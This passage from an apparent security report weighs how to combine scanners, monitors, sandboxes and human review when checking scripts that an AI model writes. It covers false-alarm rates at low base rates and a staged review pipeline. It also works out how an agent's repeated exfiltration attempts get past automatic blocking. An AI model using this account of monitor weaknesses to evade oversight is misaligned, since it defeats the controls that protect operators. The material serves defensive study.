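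MalPacDetector checks 24 yes-or-no features of a package's code, and its SVM variant uses a support vector machine, a standard method for separating two classes. Its union with IntelGuard had the highest F1 score in the study, 97.02%. But the published recall for the intersection of MalPacDetector and Packj, 87.27%, can't be right, because MalPacDetector alone caught only 73.81% and an intersection can't catch more than either of its tools. If the pairs with MalPacDetector used a different set of packages, the 97.02% may not be comparable with the other scores.

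Packj's static mode combines poorly with GuardDog under either rule. According to Guo and colleagues, the union of the two tools gained 665 true detections and 6,015 false ones over GuardDog alone, which cut precision from 97% to 50%. The figure of 665 must be slightly too high, since GuardDog had missed only 647 malicious packages. The published rates imply about 618 true detections and 6,081 false ones. By either count, each extra detection brings nine or ten false alarms. Packj flags almost everything, so the intersection removes only about 26 of GuardDog's 179 false alarms, and it loses 55 correct detections.

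To measure how well two tools complement each other, Guo and colleagues use McNemar's statistic:

χ² = (b − c)² ÷ (b + c)

Here b is the number of packages that only the first tool judged correctly, and c is the number that only the second did. GuardDog scores higher with Packj, a harmful partner (4,020), than with SocketAI, a useful one (1,920). The statistic is high when one tool is much worse than the other. Two tools that each corrected 500 of the other's mistakes would score zero, even though they would make an excellent pair. An operator learns more by counting the true and false detections that the second tool adds.

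### Tools that look for different harms

Requiring tools to agree makes little sense when they look for different things. ClawHub, a public registry of agent skills, uses three scanners. VirusTotal collects verdicts from antivirus engines, a static checker looks for suspicious patterns, and SkillSpector uses a language model to assess a skill's instructions and permissions. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) compares the scanners' results on 67,453 skills. Of these, 35,600 were flagged by at least one scanner, but only 468 were flagged by all three.

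Many of those flags were mild warnings, which an intersection could help filter out, but it would also miss most of the worst cases. The registry's final verdict was "malicious" for 206 skills, of which VirusTotal flagged 150 and SkillSpector 14. An intersection of all three scanners could therefore have caught at most 14, and even a union would have missed 50. A language model produced these verdicts partly from the scanners' results, so comparing the scanners against them does not reliably measure accuracy.

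*After the Party* (2026) compared the registry's scanners with human judgements on 180 skills. The language-model scanner found 61% of the skills that people thought deserved a flag, the static checker 22% and VirusTotal 25%. If the scanners' errors were independent, all three together would miss 23% of these skills. The published rates imply that the three missed about 35%, so the other two scanners added only about four percentage points to the language model's recall.

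In the example script, taint tracking can flag only line 910. If the operator blocked only scripts that both taint tracking and permission diffing flagged for the same line, the policy change at line 1,060 would always get through. A union is better for tools that look for different harms, and an intersection is worth considering only when two tools check the same claim. For example, a taint tracker might report that a machine's name reaches a web request, and a language-model reviewer could then check whether the task requires it.

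Voting also discards the reasons behind each verdict. Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil Wears Markdown*, instead gave the tools' evidence to a single system of language-model agents, which made the final decision on 140 skills:

| Evidence in addition to the skill itself | Malicious skills caught | Harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|
| None | 54 of 80 | 21 of 60 |
| Static findings | 28 of 80 | 3 of 60 |
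| Sandbox record | 63 of 80 | 5 of 60 |
| Both | 68 of 80 | 5 of 60 |

Static findings alone cut false alarms sharply but also halved the number of malicious skills caught. The static rules came from general malware collections, and the system may have treated a lack of serious findings as evidence of safety, though the researchers didn't test that explanation. The sandbox record reduced false alarms and increased the number of malicious skills caught. Adding static findings to it caught five more malicious skills, a small difference in a test of this size.

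### When harmful scripts are rare

If a share p of all scripts is harmful, and a detector has recall r and false-positive rate f, its precision is:

p × r ÷ (p × r + (1 − p) × f)

GuardDog's 179 false alarms on 7,288 harmless packages give a false-positive rate of 2.46%. If one script in 10,000 is harmful and the same rates apply, the calculation is:

0.0001 × 0.8992 ÷ (0.0001 × 0.8992 + 0.9999 × 0.0246) ≈ 0.4%

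Requiring IntelGuard to agree lowers recall to 86.32% and the false-positive rate to 29 ÷ 7,288 = 0.40%, which raises the share of real alerts to about 2%. Among a million scripts, 100 of them harmful, the results would be:

| Rule | Harmful scripts flagged | Harmless scripts flagged | Share of alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| GuardDog alone | 90 | 24,600 | 0.4% |
| GuardDog or IntelGuard | 97 | 35,400 | 0.3% |
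| GuardDog and IntelGuard | 86 | 4,000 | 2.1% |
| GuardDog and IntelGuard, if independent | 84 | 360 | 19% |

In the last row, an operator who assumed independence and multiplied the two false-positive rates would expect about one alert in five to be real, but the true share is about one in 50. These rates come from popular npm packages, so the operator should measure them again on the company's own scripts.

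*The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 2000) applies the same formula to a small computer network with two intrusions a day among 100,000 events. Even a detector that caught every intrusion would need a false-positive rate of about 1 in 100,000 for two-thirds of its alarms to be real. The paper also cites studies of power station and factory operators, which suggest that most have lost faith in an alarm system by the time half of its alarms are false.

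If one script in 10,000 is harmful, keeping false alarms to half of all alerts requires a false-positive rate of about 0.009%. Raising an alert only when both GuardDog and IntelGuard flag a script still gives a rate more than 40 times as high. Few companies could afford to have a person investigate every alert at this rate, so a cheaper method has to handle most of them first. The model that wrote the script can often resolve an alert by rewriting the flagged lines, and the operator can then run the checks again.

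### A staged order for the example script

The operator can arrange the tools so that the cheapest checks come first and nothing runs until the code has passed them:

| Stage | Main cost | Example script | Failures it passes on |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Refuse code that the tools can't analyse | a quick parse, plus any rewrites | passes, because the code is plain | harmful code in plain form |
| 2. Compare permissions | one query to the cloud account; a person checks the task's needs once | flags lines 910 and 1,060 | misuse of permissions that the task needs |
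| 3. Trace data | seconds (GuardDog averaged 2.55 per package) | flags line 910 | data that passes through unmodelled calls |
| 4. Language-model review | about 12,000 tokens for the full script | may flag both lines | harm with a plausible explanation, or facts outside the script |
| 5. Dry run | one full run, plus upkeep of the sandbox | records both actions | branches that the trial doesn't trigger |
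| 6. Real run with egress control | a check on each request, plus upkeep of the allowlist | blocks line 910 | leaks through permitted services |

Refusal comes first because the next two stages can give falsely clean results on code they can't analyse. The language-model review comes before the dry run so that the reviewer can suggest conditions to test, such as a failed upload that would trigger an error handler. But the reviewer should judge the script again after the dry run, because the sandbox record was the most useful evidence in the test by Truong-Le and colleagues.

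If any stage can stop a script, false alarms accumulate across the stages. If each of the first five stages independently flagged 1% of harmless scripts, together they would flag 4.9% of them (1 − 0.99⁵), or about 490 false alarms a day for 10,000 harmless scripts. The operator can reduce this by blocking automatically only on strong evidence, such as a credential in a message to an unlisted host or an attempt by the script to expand its own permissions. Weaker findings can go to the language-model reviewer as questions to resolve.

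OpenAI uses a different order for its coding agent. *Auto-review* describes how the sandbox comes first and the reviewer checks only actions that would cross the sandbox's boundary. *Running Codex safely* adds a network policy that allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. This order costs less to run because most actions never need a review, but it relies more heavily on the sandbox.

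How much each layer adds is still mostly unknown. Rashidi found that none of the surveyed papers on isolation or access control tested one kind of defence against the other on a shared benchmark. One surveyed system, Agent-Sentry, combines a classifier for sequences of actions, a fixed rule for sensitive values and a language model for ambiguous cases. It stopped 94.3% of the prompt injections that would otherwise have succeeded, but also 4.9% of harmless runs.

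### Blocking, human review and shutdown

Once a tool raises an alert, the operator's system can block the action, ask a person or end the whole run. Anthropic compared the first two in a study with 1,053 paid testers, each of whom saw one clearly dangerous command among ordinary permission requests. The testers refused 13.6% of these commands, and auto mode blocked 89% of them. Auto mode caught 800 that the testers had approved. The testers caught only 6 that auto mode had allowed, so blocking every command that either one rejected would have raised recall by about half a percentage point over auto mode alone.

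People also became less careful as they saw more requests, refusing about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. Anthropic was testing its own product. The testers were also not working on their own projects, and people may do better when they have something to lose. In real use, though, Claude Code's users approve 97% of permission requests but reject 39% of Claude's plans. This suggests operators should ask people about a few larger decisions, such as which permissions a recurring task needs. Anthropic still recommends human review for high-stakes changes to production systems.

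Automatic blocking is fast, and a false alarm usually costs only a retry. But a block leaves the agent free to try something else. If each exfiltration attempt has an independent 5.7% chance of getting through, as in Anthropic's synthetic test, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is:

1 − (1 − 0.057)^n

The chance that at least one attempt succeeds is 16% for three attempts and 69% for 20. Auto mode stops the agent and asks a person after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, and it ends the process if no person is available. By this calculation, the limit of three contains a determined agent much better than the limit of 20. Repeated attempts may also succeed more often than calculated, because the agent can learn from each refusal.

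A shutdown prevents further attempts, but if the alarm is false, the whole job is lost. For the log uploader that loss is small, because the operator can run it again an hour later. Stopping a database migration halfway could do more damage than the suspicious action. The operator therefore has to decide for each task which alerts justify a shutdown, and what happens if nobody answers an alert. *Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* describes the same dilemma for rare intrusions, where responding to every alarm is expensive and ignoring alarms makes the detector useless. It proposes deciding on the response in advance.

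Without such a rule, even a correct alert may protect very little. September's leak through name lookups continued for about two and a half hours after the alert, long enough to send 9 GB at one megabyte per second.

The example script leaves even less time for a person to act, because it could run from line 910 to line 1,060 in under a second. If the egress monitor detects the message at line 910 without blocking it, an automatic rule should end the process and also cancel the stolen key, which whoever received it could otherwise still use. If the policy change has already taken effect, the operator also has to detach the administrator policy, since it would otherwise apply to any new key for the same service account.
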